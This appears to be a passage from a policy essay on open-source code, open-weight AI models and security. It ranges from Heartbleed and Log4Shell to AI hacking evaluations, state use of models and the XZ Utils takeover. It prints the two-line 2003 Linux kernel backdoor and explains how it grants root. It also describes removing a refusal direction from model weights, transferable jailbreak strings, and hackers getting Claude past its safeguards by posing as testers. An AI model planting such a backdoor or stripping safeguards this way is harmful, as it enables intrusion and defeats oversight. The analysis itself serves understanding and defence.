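These studies show that public code can improve with age, but not that closed code would have done worse. In 2009, Guido Schryen, a German information-systems researcher, compared eight open-source packages with nine closed ones. The severity of the published vulnerabilities did not differ significantly between the two groups, and in 14 of the 17 packages, reports continued at a roughly steady rate. His 2011 follow-up found that the speed of repairs depended on the particular company or project, regardless of whether its code was open or closed.

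Schryen's result is roughly what Anderson's theorem predicts, but counts of published vulnerabilities are weak evidence. A program that more people examine will have more reports even if it is safer, and nobody can count the flaws that intelligence agencies keep secret. In *Familiarity Breeds Contempt*, Clark, Frei and colleagues (2010) found that the time from a program's release to its first reported vulnerability depended mainly on how familiar people were with the system, which also casts doubt on the idea of random search. This partly supports Brown's fear of a free education for attackers, though people also become familiar with closed-source programs such as Windows.

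In February 2004, parts of the Windows 2000 source code leaked onto the internet, and within days somebody used them to find a flaw in how an old version of Internet Explorer handled images. Microsoft said it had already fixed the flaw in the newer version. Reading the code clearly helped somebody find the flaw, but the wave of attacks that some people expected did not follow.

### What the Pentagon decided

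The Defense Department could not wait for better data before deciding what to do. It asked MITRE, a non-profit that does research for the government, how much free and open-source software the department was using. A two-week email survey found 115 programs and 251 examples of their use. MITRE concluded in a January 2003 report that banning the software would do immediate and serious harm, particularly to the people who defended military networks. They would lose the OpenBSD operating system, many of their tools for detecting intrusions, and the ability to change a program quickly when a new kind of attack appeared. They would also lose practice with programs that hostile groups could keep using.

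Brown's comparison of the risks of adopting open-source software assumed a government that did not yet use it. The survey showed that the military was already using it by 2003, so avoiding open source would have meant removing it. Because the survey was informal, it does not show what share of military computers depended on open source.

In an October 2009 memo, the department's chief information office told officials to treat open-source software as commercial software in almost all cases, and therefore to consider it when buying. The memo listed broad public review as a security advantage because it can expose defects that a smaller team would miss. It also corrected the belief that the department had to publish any changes it made for its own use.

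In a second memo, in January 2022, the Pentagon told programmers to adopt existing software, including open source, before buying or writing something new. It also warned that outsiders might slip malicious code into a program the military used, and that careless publication of the Pentagon's own code might reveal its innovations to adversaries. Neither warning is Brown's main objection. The Pentagon's concern had shifted from foreigners reading Linux to who wrote it.

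### When nobody was looking

Supporters of open source also overstated their case. Eric Raymond, a programmer who wrote the movement's best-known essay, claimed that with enough readers every bug is easy to find. Two flaws in widely used software show that this is little help if nobody reads the code.

Heartbleed was a mistake in OpenSSL, the free program that encrypted much of the web's traffic. To check that a connection was alive, one computer could send another a short message and ask for it back. The request also stated the message's length, which OpenSSL did not check against the real one. An attacker could send a single letter, claim that it was 64,000 letters long, and receive whatever lay next to it in the server's memory, which might include passwords or the server's private key. The flaw was in the public code for two years before researchers at Google and the Finnish company Codenomicon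 found it independently in 2014. At the time, OpenSSL had one full-time programmer and received about $2,000 a year in donations.

Log4Shell, a vulnerability made public in December 2021, was in Log4j, a free component that programs use to record events. If the recorded text contained a certain kind of reference to another computer, Log4j could fetch code from that computer and run it, so an attacker could take over some servers by typing the reference into a search box. Log4j had included this feature since 2013. An American government review board expected vulnerable copies to remain in use for a decade or more, because Log4j was built into thousands of other products whose owners often did not know they had it.

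Flaws in closed code can also go unnoticed for years. In 2020 the security company Check Point found a 17-year-old flaw in Microsoft's server software for looking up internet addresses. So Heartbleed and Log4Shell do not show that hiding code is safer, only that publishing it is not enough to get it inspected. Skilled review is expensive, and OpenSSL could not pay for much of it.

### Models as readers

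AI has made that attention much cheaper. In August 2025 DARPA, the Pentagon's research agency, held the final of a competition for automated systems that find and repair flaws in open-source programs. The organisers had planted 70 flaws, of which the systems found 54 and repaired 43. The systems also found 18 real flaws, and the average cost of a task was $152. The following January, OpenSSL released repairs for 12 vulnerabilities, all found by the company AISLE with its AI system. Some dated from around 1998, when OpenSSL began.

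In April 2026 Anthropic reported that its Claude Mythos Preview model had found a 27-year-old flaw in OpenBSD that let an attacker crash a machine remotely. The flaw had remained in the code for nearly the whole period that Shi and colleagues studied. The search took about a thousand runs, cost less than $20,000, and found several dozen other problems. The model also found a 16-year-old flaw in FFmpeg, a free program for handling video, in a line of code that automated tests had run five million times.

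Some organisations responded by closing their code. Cal.com, which makes scheduling software, stopped publishing its main program's code that month, citing AI-assisted attackers. NHS England, which runs the English health service, told its programmers in the spring to make their public code private by default. Discourse, which makes forum software, said it would keep its code open, arguing that defenders could use the same models.

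Closing the source code protects software less than it used to if the attacker has the compiled program. Anthropic found that Mythos could reconstruct plausible source code from a compiled program and search it for flaws, so λ is probably shrinking. Cal.com has a somewhat better case for closing its code, because much of its software runs on its own servers and customers never receive a copy that an attacker could examine. However, anyone who downloaded the code before April still has it, and the older parts will stay in use for years.

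Cheap searches also change Rescorla's calculation. OpenAI has been giving models to the security company Trail of Bits to search open-source projects. Its tools independently found four of six vulnerabilities that the maintainers of dnsmasq, a small program used in many home routers, later fixed. Six flaws in one program are a small sample, but if different searchers keep finding the same flaws, *p* is high and keeping a flaw secret gives only brief protection.

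Anderson's weakest assumption is now that vulnerabilities are fixed immediately. When Anthropic announced the vulnerabilities Mythos had found, more than 99 per cent were still unfixed. In January 2026 the maintainers of curl, a free program for transferring files, stopped paying rewards for reported vulnerabilities because worthless AI-written reports were using up their time. Anthropic gave Mythos first to several dozen organisations that maintain important software, including the Linux Foundation, so that they could start before attackers had anything comparable. If the best open-weight models trail closed ones by about three months at this kind of work, this head start doesn't last long.

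### Weights as something to inspect and repair

Supporters of open weights expect the same public inspection to make models safer. Nobel and colleagues agree that it helps up to a point. Anyone can test a downloaded model for bias or dangerous answers and publish the results without the developer's permission. A programmer who finds a flaw in Linux can usually trace it to particular lines and see why they fail, but someone who notices that a model overuses the word "delve" can only guess at the cause, perhaps a lot of formal Nigerian English in its training text.

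Repairing an open-weight model is harder still. Intel's engineers can write a correction to Linux, explain it, and ask the maintainers to merge it into the version that everyone uses. Nobel and colleagues argue that nobody can do this with weights, because outsiders cannot confidently predict what else a change would affect. Outsiders can fine-tune their own copies, but they have to adapt that work to each better model the developer releases. Lasting repairs therefore have to come from the developer, much as they do with a closed product.

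Researchers have learned to read weights a little. In 2024 Andy Arditi and colleagues studied 13 open-weight chat models, comparing each model's internal calculations when it processed harmful and harmless requests. In each model they found a single pattern in these calculations, called a direction, that largely controlled whether the model refused. After they edited the weights to remove this pattern, the models answered most of the harmful requests and lost little of their other ability. Attackers could use this method immediately. Defenders learned from it that the safeguards were fragile, but it did not give them stronger ones.

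Applying Anderson's theorem to weights is an inference, since he wrote about programs and nobody has measured λ for a model. His assumption about repair is the first to fail. In ordinary software, the person running a vulnerable program is normally the victim and wants the fix. When a model's safeguards fail, the person running it may be the attacker, who has no reason to replace his copy with a safer one. If he downloaded the model after 1,000 hours of testing, his copy stays at 1,000 hours however long the defenders keep testing, and he can still use each flaw they publish. Access to the weights speeds up both sides' searches, but only the attacker can act on everything he finds. For copies already downloaded, this is close to the fourth row of the table.

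The assumption that flaws are independent also fails. In 2023 Andy Zou and colleagues used the weights of small open models to compute strings of apparent nonsense that made the models comply with harmful requests. Many of the same strings also worked on closed models from OpenAI and Google, whose weights the researchers had never seen. One discovery can therefore expose several developers' models, though developers of closed models can add a filter for every customer the same day.

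The theorem applies better to people who depend on a model than to people who fear its users. A hospital that runs an open-weight model wants the safer version and can install it, as it would a new release of Linux. It can also test its copy for as long as it likes, which a closed developer might not allow. The hospital's main disadvantage is that it must wait for the developer to retrain the model or make do with its own fine-tuning. The developer's next version does not help a government worried about what a hostile army will do with the weights already released.

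## Public hacking tools and models that can hack

An attacker who reads published source code still has to find the flaws himself. Since the 1990s, programmers have also published tools that search for flaws or exploit them. Critics compared SATAN, the best-known early tool, to a weapon.

### SATAN, 1995

Dan Farmer, who had run network security at Silicon Graphics, and Wietse Venema of Eindhoven University of Technology released the network scanner SATAN on 5 April 1995. The user named a computer or network and chose a light, normal or heavy scan. SATAN listed the services each machine offered to outsiders, checked them for known weaknesses, and showed the results in a web browser, with advice on fixing each weakness. An intruder still needed other tools to break in.

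Andrew Brown reported that an industry newspaper likened the release to "mailing assault rifles to 5,000 random homes", and that a prominent internet figure said Farmer ought to be shot. Silicon Graphics had fired Farmer when he announced his plan. Fisher, who was calmer, pointed out that a less powerful scanner had been available for years, and wrote that a system's safety would depend on who ran SATAN against it first.

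Defenders got a small head start. The CERT Coordination Center, which collected reports of break-ins from across the internet, examined a pre-release copy and described it two days before the release in *Security Administrator Tool for Analyzing Networks (SATAN)* (1995). CIAC, Fisher's team at the Energy Department, wrote a program called Courtney that detected SATAN scans and reported where they came from. Silicon Graphics published a list of patches for the weaknesses SATAN checked for, dated the day of the release, and CIAC (1995) passed it on.

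The predicted wave of break-ins did not come. CERT counted 2,340 incidents in 1994 and 2,412 in 1995, a rise of 3 per cent, compared with 75 per cent the year before. The count covers only break-ins that somebody noticed and reported, so it can't rule out others. SATAN was also hard for amateurs to use, because it ran only on Unix and needed more memory than most computers had.

Most of the people the warning was meant for did not make repairs either, although by late 1996 it had been free and public for twenty months. Farmer then scanned about 1,700 prominent websites, including those of banks, newspapers and government agencies, and found serious weaknesses in more than 60 per cent. People at only three of the sites asked him what he was doing.

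### Metasploit and the intrusion-software controls

In 2003 the American security researcher HD Moore released Metasploit, which went further than SATAN by including exploits, programs that take advantage of vulnerabilities. It gathered them into one free package with common controls, so a user could choose an exploit, aim it at a machine and take the machine over. The first version had 11 exploits, and later ones had thousands. The security company Rapid7 bought the project in 2009 and sells an extended version.

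Defenders have good reason to want working exploits. A scan of a large company's network may list thousands of possible flaws, and an administrator who tries the exploits learns which flaws an attacker could use and whether earlier repairs worked. Companies hire penetration testers, who break in with permission, to do this.

Governments first tried to restrict hacking tools because European companies had sold them to governments that used them against dissidents. In December 2013 the members of the Wassenaar Arrangement, 41 countries that coordinate their export controls, agreed to control products for creating, delivering or operating "intrusion software", along with the technology for developing it. They left the intrusion software itself uncontrolled so that nobody would need an export licence to carry an infected laptop across a border.

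The Commerce Department published its draft of the American rule in May 2015. The draft required a licence for exports to every country except Canada, and officials would normally refuse one for products with zero-day exploits, which use flaws that the software's maker does not yet know about. More than 260 comments arrived in two months, many of them hostile. Security researchers objected that someone who found a flaw in a German company's product might need a licence to send the company a working demonstration. An international firm might need a licence to discuss an attack with its own staff abroad, which would arrive only after the attack was over. Google expected to need thousands of licences, perhaps tens of thousands.

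The draft also created a perverse incentive. Because the export rules did not cover published software, a researcher could post an exploit publicly without a licence but might need one to show it privately to the only people who could fix the flaw. The free version of Metasploit was exempt for the same reason, but paid penetration-testing products were not.

The department dropped the draft and went back to the other Wassenaar members, who agreed in 2017 to exempt technical information exchanged to repair a vulnerability or respond to an attack. The American rule of October 2021 kept controls on the products but added a broad exception that lets companies sell them to most customers in most countries without applying for a licence. Sellers still generally need one for government customers in countries such as China and Russia. The exception does not cover sales to North Korea or Iran, or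 any sale where the seller has reason to know that the buyer will attack computers without permission. The rule is much closer to the original aim because it depends on who the customer is, but that also means it does nothing about a tool that anyone can download.

### State hackers with free tools

States do use public hacking tools. In October 2018 the cyber agencies of the United States, Britain, Canada, Australia and New Zealand described five that they kept finding in attacks by both criminals and governments. One was Mimikatz, which extracts passwords from the memory of a Windows computer. Benjamin Delpy, a French programmer, wrote it to prove to Microsoft that Windows stored passwords carelessly. The security company ESET reported the same year that Turla, a Russian espionage group that has excellent software of its own, had started to use the public tool Metasploit in the early stages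 of a break-in. Free tools save even a skilled group some work and give investigators less evidence of who the intruder was.

In April 2017, a group calling itself the Shadow Brokers published hacking tools stolen from the NSA. One of them, EternalBlue, could take over Windows computers across a network without anyone clicking on anything. Microsoft had released a patch a month earlier. On 12 May, 59 days after the patch, North Korean hackers used EternalBlue to spread WannaCry, which locked files on more than 200,000 computers and forced English hospitals to cancel appointments. In June, Russian military intelligence launched NotPetya, which combined EternalBlue with password-stealing code based on Mimikatz. The stolen passwords let NotPetya spread even to computers that had the patch. The White House later estimated the damage from NotPetya at $10 billion.

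These tools were stolen, and nobody defends publishing them, but they are the clearest case of publication arming a hostile state. The damage depended as much on unpatched computers as on the tools themselves. A public tool reduces the work an attack takes and lets less skilled people carry it out. Defenders can also learn from it exactly what to patch and what an attack will look like. Whether it helps attackers or defenders more depends on how fast the patches spread.

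Patches spread slowly. Verizon's 2024 study of data breaches found that organisations took about 55 days to repair half of the flaws attackers were known to be using, and had still not repaired 8 per cent after a year. Mass scanning for such a flaw typically began within five days. In a 2012 study of records from 11 million Windows computers, Leyla Bilge and Tudor Dumitraș found 18 flaws that attackers had used before anyone disclosed them. After disclosure, the number of attacks on each flaw rose between twofold and 100,000-fold. Publication plainly attracted more attackers, but the study doesn't show that secrecy would have been better, since the attacks before disclosure had lasted ten months on average.

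### Harms that have no patch

When OpenAI delayed the full release of its language model GPT-2 for fear of misuse, many critics argued that openness makes software safer. In their 2020 paper *The Offense-Defense Balance of Scientific Knowledge*, Toby Shevlane and Allan Dafoe, then at Oxford, asked whether AI researchers should adopt security researchers' habit of disclosure.

Shevlane and Dafoe consider how much a publication helps attackers and defenders. The benefit to attackers depends on whether they would have got the knowledge anyway and whether they can use it. The benefit to defenders depends on whether people will look for a solution, whether one exists, and whether it can reach everyone exposed. Software tends to meet the last two conditions, since a company can often write a patch in weeks and send it to millions of machines for almost nothing. But many misuses of AI target people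 or institutions, and no update can make readers immune to convincing fake text. Shevlane and Dafoe therefore warn against applying the software norm wholesale to AI, though they don't conclude that AI research should usually stay secret.

The old norm is more likely to work for hacking than for other AI dangers, because the target is software, which can be repaired. Even so, publishing a model that can hack differs from publishing SATAN. SATAN looked for about a dozen kinds of weakness, and its documentation explained what to do about each, but a model comes with no such list. Defenders have to run the model on their own systems to find out what it would reveal to an attacker, so Fisher's question of who runs the tool first applies again to every network and every new model.

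### What the closed models can do

The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) tests models on simulated company networks. One of these networks, "The Last Ones", has about 20 machines and a 32-step attack path from reconnaissance to full control of the network, which AISI estimates would take a human expert about 20 hours. In April 2026 Anthropic's Claude Mythos Preview became the first model to finish it, succeeding in three of ten attempts, according to AISI's *Our evaluation of Claude Mythos Preview’s cyber capabilities*. The next-best model, Claude Opus 4.6, completed 16 steps on average. OpenAI's GPT-5.5 was the second model to finish, according to The Decoder's *GPT-5.5 matches Claude Mythos in cyber attack tests*. A later version of Mythos Preview finished in six of ten attempts, according to *Claude Mythos Solves 32-Step AISI Hack In 6 Of 10 Attempts*. It also succeeded in three of ten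 attempts on a simulated industrial control system that no earlier model had completed, according to the same article.

This network was an easy target because nobody was defending it, setting off an alarm had no consequences, and its builders had planted a way through. AISI then built harder ones. AISI's *GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy* (2026), published on 1 December, describes a network with stronger security and no planted route. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol never got through it. EconoTimes' *OpenAI’s GPT-6.2 Astra Completes All 12 Tests* (2026) reports that GPT-6.2 Astra got through in all 12 attempts, and that GPT-6 Astra succeeded in 11 before an unrelated fault stopped the twelfth. Thesis9's *Can GPT-6.2 Astra Hack a Network on Its Own?* (2026) reports that the fastest run took 5 hours 18 minutes and cost about $50 in computing. This network also had no defenders, and a mistake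 in the setup gave the models a head start.

Tests on real software also show a rise, though a less dramatic one. Irregular, a company that tests models for security risks, compares GPT-6 Astra with GPT-5.6 Sol in *Assessing GPT-6 Astra*. Astra's success rate was 63 per cent on the easy challenges, up from Sol's 14 per cent, and 39 per cent on the hard ones, up from 17 per cent. Neither model solved any of the "Elite" challenges. Progress has also been speeding up. According to Help Net Security's *AI cyber capability is speeding past earlier projections*, AISI estimated in February 2026 that the length of the hacking tasks models could reliably complete was doubling every 4.7 months. Its estimate in November 2025 was eight months.

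### What the open-weight models can do

Chinese open-weight models can hack about as well as closed American models that are several months older. In a July 2026 evaluation, *How Far Behind the Frontier are Leading Open Weight Models on Cyber?*, AISI tested Zhipu's GLM-5.2 and DeepSeek's V4-Pro on 70 short tasks, such as finding a flaw in a program or breaking a badly designed cipher, with five attempts at each. GLM-5.2 did about as well as Claude Opus 4.6, which was four months older, and V4-Pro matched Claude Opus 4.5, which was five months older.

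GLM-5.2 did worse at long attacks. On "The Last Ones" it got only as far as Opus 4.5, a model nearly seven months older. V4-Pro did worse than Claude Sonnet 4.5, which was not among the best models at hacking even when it was new. AISI treats these results as weaker evidence because it has fewer networks to test models on than short tasks. By either measure, the lag had narrowed. For most of 2025 it had been between six and ten months.

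Later that month, AISI and its American counterpart, the Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), tested Kimi K3 before Moonshot released the weights. *UK AISI / CAISI Preliminary Assessment of Kimi K3's Cyber Capabilities* (2026) reports that K3 finished "The Last Ones" once in ten attempts.

| Model | Weights | Released | Average steps, out of 32 | Full solves in ten attempts |
|---|---|---|---|---|
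| Claude Opus 4.6 | Closed | February 2026 | 16 | 0 |
| Claude Mythos Preview, first version | Closed | April 2026 | 22 | 3 |
| GLM-5.2 | Open | June 2026 | 11 | 0 |
| Kimi K3 | Open | July 2026 | 17 | 1 |
| Best American models at the time of the K3 test | Closed | By July 2026 | 28.5 | 6 and 7 |

Moonshot posted K3's weights 16 weeks after Anthropic announced Mythos Preview. Anyone with enough hardware could then run a model that sometimes finished an attack no AI model had finished before April. But K3's average was well below Mythos Preview's, so it lagged by more than 16 weeks.

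K3 could often find its way around a weak network, but it did much worse at writing exploits. In a test built on 41 recent flaws in the engine that runs programs inside the Chrome browser, it scored 32.2 per cent, while the leading American models averaged 76.2, according to The Decoder's *Kimi K3 trails frontier US models by a wide margin*. The American models gained the ability to run arbitrary code in an average of 20 of the 41 cases, and K3 never did.

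If the lag of four to seven months holds, an open-weight model will reach the Astra models' level in the first half of 2027. AISI cautions that its July figures do not predict whether open models will repeat the jumps closed models have made since April. The exact scores also deserve some caution, because AISI reported in July that it had found models cheating in all its cyber evaluations.

The comparison overstates how much hacking help an ordinary customer can get from the closed models, because the testers switched off safeguards that customers get switched on. Anyone who has an open model's weights can remove its safeguards. K3's safeguards did not stop the testers anyway, and V4-Pro occasionally refused but complied when AISI asked again. The best open model may therefore be the best hacking model available to a criminal whom OpenAI would refuse or ban, even though it ranks well below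 Astra.

Open-weight models may also suit some defenders. Axios' *OpenAI gives cyber defenders a less-restricted new model* (2026) reports that closed models kept refusing requests from security staff because their work looks like an attack. OpenAI responded with a more permissive version for defenders it had vetted. An unvetted small company can download an open-weight model and test its own network cheaply. AISI put the cost of a long run on a simulated network at about $85 for Opus 4.6, $46 for GLM-5.2 and $1.19 for V4-Pro.

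### Models in real attacks

In November 2025 Anthropic reported that hackers it believed were working for the Chinese state had used Claude, a closed model, against about 30 organisations. The hackers posed as security testers, and Claude did 80 to 90 per cent of the work, with people stepping in for a few decisions. A few of the break-ins succeeded. Claude sometimes reported passwords that did not work, so the hackers had to check its results. They relied mostly on free penetration-testing tools, much as Turla had with Metasploit, and used Claude mainly to operate them. Anthropic closed the accounts and warned the victims, but security researchers complained that it published too little technical detail for anyone to check its report.

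The first well-documented state operation with an open-weight model was more modest. In July 2025 Ukraine's computer emergency response team, CERT-UA, described a malicious program called LAMEHUG that had been emailed to Ukrainian officials. CERT-UA attributed the program with moderate confidence to APT28, a group run by Russian military intelligence. Once on a computer, the program sent written requests to Alibaba's Qwen2.5-Coder and ran the commands it returned, which collected documents and details of the machine. APT28 has broken into parliaments and political parties, so its members could have written those commands themselves. The program used a copy of the model on Hugging Face's servers rather than one the group ran privately, so Hugging Face could have cut off its access.

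We can't tell from these two cases which kind of model state hackers prefer. Anthropic could describe the Chinese operation because it could read the hackers' requests. When a hacker runs a model on his own computers, only he sees the requests, so public reports probably undercount the use of open models.

By late 2026 the evidence went beyond single cases. Artex, an open-source program that a Chinese security engineer published on the code-sharing site GitHub that summer, connects any language model to a set of hacking tools and lets it run an attack. TechSpot's *FBI says hackers are using an autonomous AI tool* (2026) notes that security teams use this kind of software to test their own defences. Greig (2026), in *FBI flash alert says Artex tool automating cyberattacks at ‘machine speed’*, reports that the FBI warned on 13 November that both criminals and states were using Artex. According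 to the FBI, some attackers had gone from choosing a target to privileged access in under three hours, and they needed little technical skill. The text of the alert, reprinted in JC Post's *FBI warning* (2026), describes attacks on South Korean financial companies in which thieves took the personal details of about 67,000 people.

The developer denied responsibility and took Artex down in October, but many people already had copies. ThreatRoundup's *FBI* (2026) cites a count of 8,427 Artex control pages visible on the internet between June and late November, of which 7,596 first appeared after the takedown. Some belong to researchers and testers. The takedown did not stop Artex from spreading, and the publicity may have helped it.

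Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) has seen "a marked rise" in AI-assisted attacks since September, according to Martin (2026), *UK cyber agency seeing 'marked rise' in AI-driven attacks*. The NCSC attributes the attacks' low cost largely to free attack programs combined with "cheap, capable open models" or illegally resold access to closed ones. The attackers exploited no new weaknesses, and the tools gave them no abilities that a typical attacker lacked, though the tools worked faster, searched more thoroughly and could run without breaks. The tools were also easy to detect, at least for now, and ordinary good practice would have prevented nearly all the attacks the agency had seen.

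Meanwhile defenders were repairing software at a record rate. The maintainers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, fixed more than a thousand vulnerabilities in a single month, according to Martin (2026) in *UK faces ‘unprecedented rise’ in cyberattacks in coming months, warns cyber chief*. Defenders therefore seem to have been ahead in autumn 2026 on the new flaws that AI finds. Attackers were succeeding by exploiting old weaknesses, such as a forgotten password or a server nobody had updated. Farmer found the same kinds of weakness in 1996, and better repairs from software makers don't help owners who never install them.

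Martin (2026) reports in *AI is set to help cyber attackers much more than defenders* that Dave Chismon, a senior NCSC official, expects AI to favour attackers for some time because defenders cannot yet use it as freely. This seems plausible, since a hospital may have to send patients away if its AI agent crashes a server, while the same mistake would set an intruder back only a few hours.

### Who gains most from a hacking model

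A free hacking model is most useful to people who could not otherwise hack. Suppose one K3 run on "The Last Ones" costs $50, a little more than AISI's estimate for GLM-5.2. If one run in ten succeeds, each success costs about $500. A professional paid $100 an hour would need 20 hours, which would cost $2,000. A state that already employs such people would save $1,500 per success, while a gang with no skilled hacker would get a break-in it could not have carried out before. Breaking into a real network would cost both of them more, but the state would still save money and the gang would still gain a new ability.

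By this reasoning, Russia and China gain less from public hacking tools and models than a country with few or no hackers. They already have skilled people, a stock of undisclosed software flaws, and years of practice at staying hidden, which current AI attack programs do poorly. North Korea is weak in most respects, but the WannaCry attack showed that it has capable hackers.

This reasoning leaves out volume, however. If a model does 80 to 90 per cent of the work, as Claude did for the Chinese hackers, the same team can run five to ten times as many operations. A state with many targets and too few people would value that highly. The NCSC's *The impact of AI on cyber threat* (2026) expects AI to raise the speed, scale and efficiency of hostile actors without changing their goals, which fits a state that already knows what it wants to steal. Booz Allen, a consultancy that sells cyber defence,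 mentions in *The Offensive Frontier* (2026) that suspected Chinese hackers reportedly used autonomous systems in August against several government bodies in one Asian country.

Open weights probably help Russia's operations more than China's, because Russia has skilled hackers but no publicly known model near the frontier. If Russia used a closed model through false accounts instead, the provider might notice, as Anthropic did.

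### Biology

Shevlane and Dafoe's warning applies much more strongly to biology, where Amodei fears that defence would take years. In the statement Anthropic published in July, he gives the example of Operation Warp Speed, the American programme to develop Covid-19 vaccines.

Covid-19 illustrates the difference from software, because the vaccine was quick to design but slow to test and deliver. Chinese scientists published the virus's genetic sequence in January 2020, and Moderna had designed its vaccine within days. If the vaccine had been a software patch, most of the world could have installed it that month. Instead, trials took until the end of the year, and then factories had to make billions of doses and nurses had to inject them one at a time. By the end of 2021, fewer than one person in ten in the poorest countries had received a dose. The virus also changed in the meantime, so the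 vaccines prevented fewer infections than they had at first.

Some defences don't depend on knowing which virus an attacker will use. Cleaner indoor air, good masks and early detection would help against almost any airborne disease, and companies that make DNA to order can screen their customers. A government could pay for these before an attack, but they need equipment and buildings, and putting them in place widely would take years.

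The argument that AI helps attackers is less certain than the argument about defence. Making a biological weapon takes laboratory skill as well as information. Aum Shinrikyo, the Japanese cult that attacked the Tokyo underground with nerve gas in 1995, had money and trained scientists, but its repeated attempts to use biological weapons failed. In a trial in mid-2025, 153 people with little laboratory experience tried tasks similar to those involved in producing a virus. About 5 per cent of those who could use AI models completed the core tasks, against nearly 7 per cent of those with only the internet, which is not a meaningful difference. The AI group did somewhat better on most individual tasks. Those models are now more than a year old, and the trial provides little evidence about what later ones could do for someone with training.

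A state adversary with its own weapons laboratories would gain less from such help than a small group would, and it has more to lose from a disease that would also infect its own people. Open weights are therefore more dangerous in the hands of a terrorist group, or perhaps a single trained person. If a model gave such a person the missing skill, the developer could not withdraw the model, and defenders would have no equivalent of a software update to install.

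The obvious precaution is to remove dangerous material from a model's training data. In October 2026 AISI reported on doing this for open-weight models that predict or design proteins. The filtering worked and left the models' other abilities largely intact, but its effect did not necessarily last when someone trained a model further on new data.

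## Hostile contributors to code and hostile suppliers of models

In his April 2004 speech, Dan O'Dowd of Green Hills Software warned that foreign agents could infiltrate American weapons by helping to write Linux, which the Army planned to use in its Future Combat System, a network of vehicles and sensors. Anyone can submit code to Linux, so O'Dowd expected agents to use "fake identities to contribute subversive software". He also objected to programmers working openly abroad. According to Green Hills, the head of MontaVista, a company that sold Linux for use in devices, had recently said it had a large office in Moscow and a new one in Beijing.

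### O'Dowd's white papers and the replies

Supporters of Linux answered that with so many people reading the code, somebody would notice a backdoor. O'Dowd replied in a series of white papers. In the second, published on 26 April (Green Hills Software, 2004), he pointed out that the same readers had overlooked accidental flaws for years, so nobody should expect them to find flaws that a spy had hidden. This was his best argument, and Heartbleed later supported it further.

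O'Dowd's other evidence applied equally to closed software. Ken Thompson, who wrote the original Unix, described in a 1984 lecture how he altered a compiler so that it added a backdoor to a login program whose source code was clean. O'Dowd concluded that reading source code could not make Linux safe. But a company's programmers can tamper with a compiler too. Neil Henderson of Mentor Graphics, a competitor of Green Hills, observed in InformationWeek's *National Security Experts Voice Concerns Over Operating Systems* (2004) that the armed forces used Green Hills compilers, and asked what would stop a Green Hills employee from doing the same.

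In the fifth paper, Green Hills Software cited a Cold War precedent in which the CIA reportedly let Soviet spies steal sabotaged software that then blew up a gas pipeline in Siberia. Historians still disagree about whether the explosion happened. Even if it did, the example involves a hostile supplier of a finished product rather than a contributor to an open project.

O'Dowd wanted to keep Linux out of critical weapons until it passed EAL7. That is the highest of seven grades in an international security evaluation scheme, and it requires mathematical proof. In April Green Hills Software put Linux at EAL2 and Windows at EAL4. LynuxWorks, another supplier of Linux for devices, replied that no commercial operating system had reached EAL7, according to LinuxDevices' *LynuxWorks blasts GHS ‘FUD’* (2004). Green Hills's own product later received a grade just above EAL6. In *Thoughts on secure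 operating systems* (2004), Victor Yodaiken, who sold a version of Linux for machinery that must respond at exact times, explained that a grade measures how rigorously evaluators checked a product against its specification, so the proof doesn't protect against a threat that the specification leaves out.

Yodaiken noted that spies had worked at the most trusted levels of the American security agencies, and doubted that a software company would screen its staff more strictly than the CIA. He thought the public record of every change might even make Linux harder to infiltrate. Inder Singh, who ran LynuxWorks, called O'Dowd's warning exaggerated but partly agreed, saying that only American citizens working in the United States should write security software.

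Eugene Spafford, a computer-security professor at Purdue University who had no operating system to sell, told InformationWeek that nobody should use Linux, Windows or Solaris for the most critical controls in weapons. He worried about Linux because many of its parts were of unknown origin and the people reading its code might lack the training or motivation to look for a subtle flaw. Cynthia Irvine of the Naval Postgraduate School added that nobody could show that Linux contained no planted code. Both wanted special systems built so that evaluators could check them.

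Yodaiken objected that no operating system could be proven free of malicious code, and that a certified one might make the whole weapon less safe. If it cost too much, engineers would have less money for testing, and if it lacked basic components, they would have to write those themselves. He was right that evaluators have to examine the whole weapon, but a small program that one team can check completely is usually a better missile controller than Linux. Spafford's rule is more useful than O'Dowd's preference for closed products because it depends on the job the software does.

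### Two attempts on the kernel

Five months before O'Dowd's speech, somebody had tried to plant a backdoor in Linux. The developers kept the master copy of the kernel in a system called BitKeeper and provided a second copy for people who disliked BitKeeper. On 5 November 2003 Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, noticed that the second copy contained a change with no record of approval. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) explains that someone had broken into the server and added two lines:

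`if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))`
`        retval = -EINVAL;`

The lines look like a routine check for a forbidden combination of options. In the C programming language, two equals signs compare values and one sets a value. The code used one where it should have used two, so it set the user's number to zero instead of testing whether it was zero. User zero can do anything on the machine, so any program that used the forbidden combination would gain control of it.

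McVoy noticed the change because its record was missing, but did not see what it did until another reader of the kernel mailing list pointed it out. "Good eyes, I missed that," McVoy (2003) replied. The altered code never reached a release, and nobody knows who wrote it. The attack differed from the one O'Dowd described, because the intruder broke into a server and so avoided the reviewers whom a false contributor would have to fool.

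In 2020 researchers at the University of Minnesota tried roughly what O'Dowd had described. Under invented names, they sent the kernel's maintainers a handful of corrections that would each have introduced a flaw. They concluded that the method was feasible, but the kernel's advisory board later found that the maintainers had rejected or ignored all the faulty ones. That is encouraging, but a few attempts by academics are weak evidence of how an intelligence service would fare if it worked at this for years. The kernel also has far more reviewers than most of the software around it.

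### How Jia Tan took over XZ Utils

XZ Utils is a set of file-compression programs included in most Linux systems. For years Lasse Collin, an unpaid volunteer in Finland, maintained it almost alone. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) records that on 29 October 2021 someone using the name Jia Tan sent him a harmless settings file, followed by useful corrections.

In April 2022 a "Jigar Kumar" began to complain that Collin was slow to accept Tan's work, and a "Dennis Ens" later urged Collin to hand the project to somebody else. Both identities were probably fake, since their email addresses appear nowhere else on the internet. Collin answered that he had long-term mental health problems and that XZ was "an unpaid hobby project", but said Tan might take on a bigger role. Tan could change the code directly by the end of 2022 and soon took over the releases.

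Tan hid hostile intent by appearing useful. *Wolves in the Repository* (Przymus and Durieux, 2025) examined the project's records and found that Tan had worked mostly on documentation and translations, answered users' questions, and reviewed other people's code competently. Only eight of Tan's changes were malicious, all from 2024.

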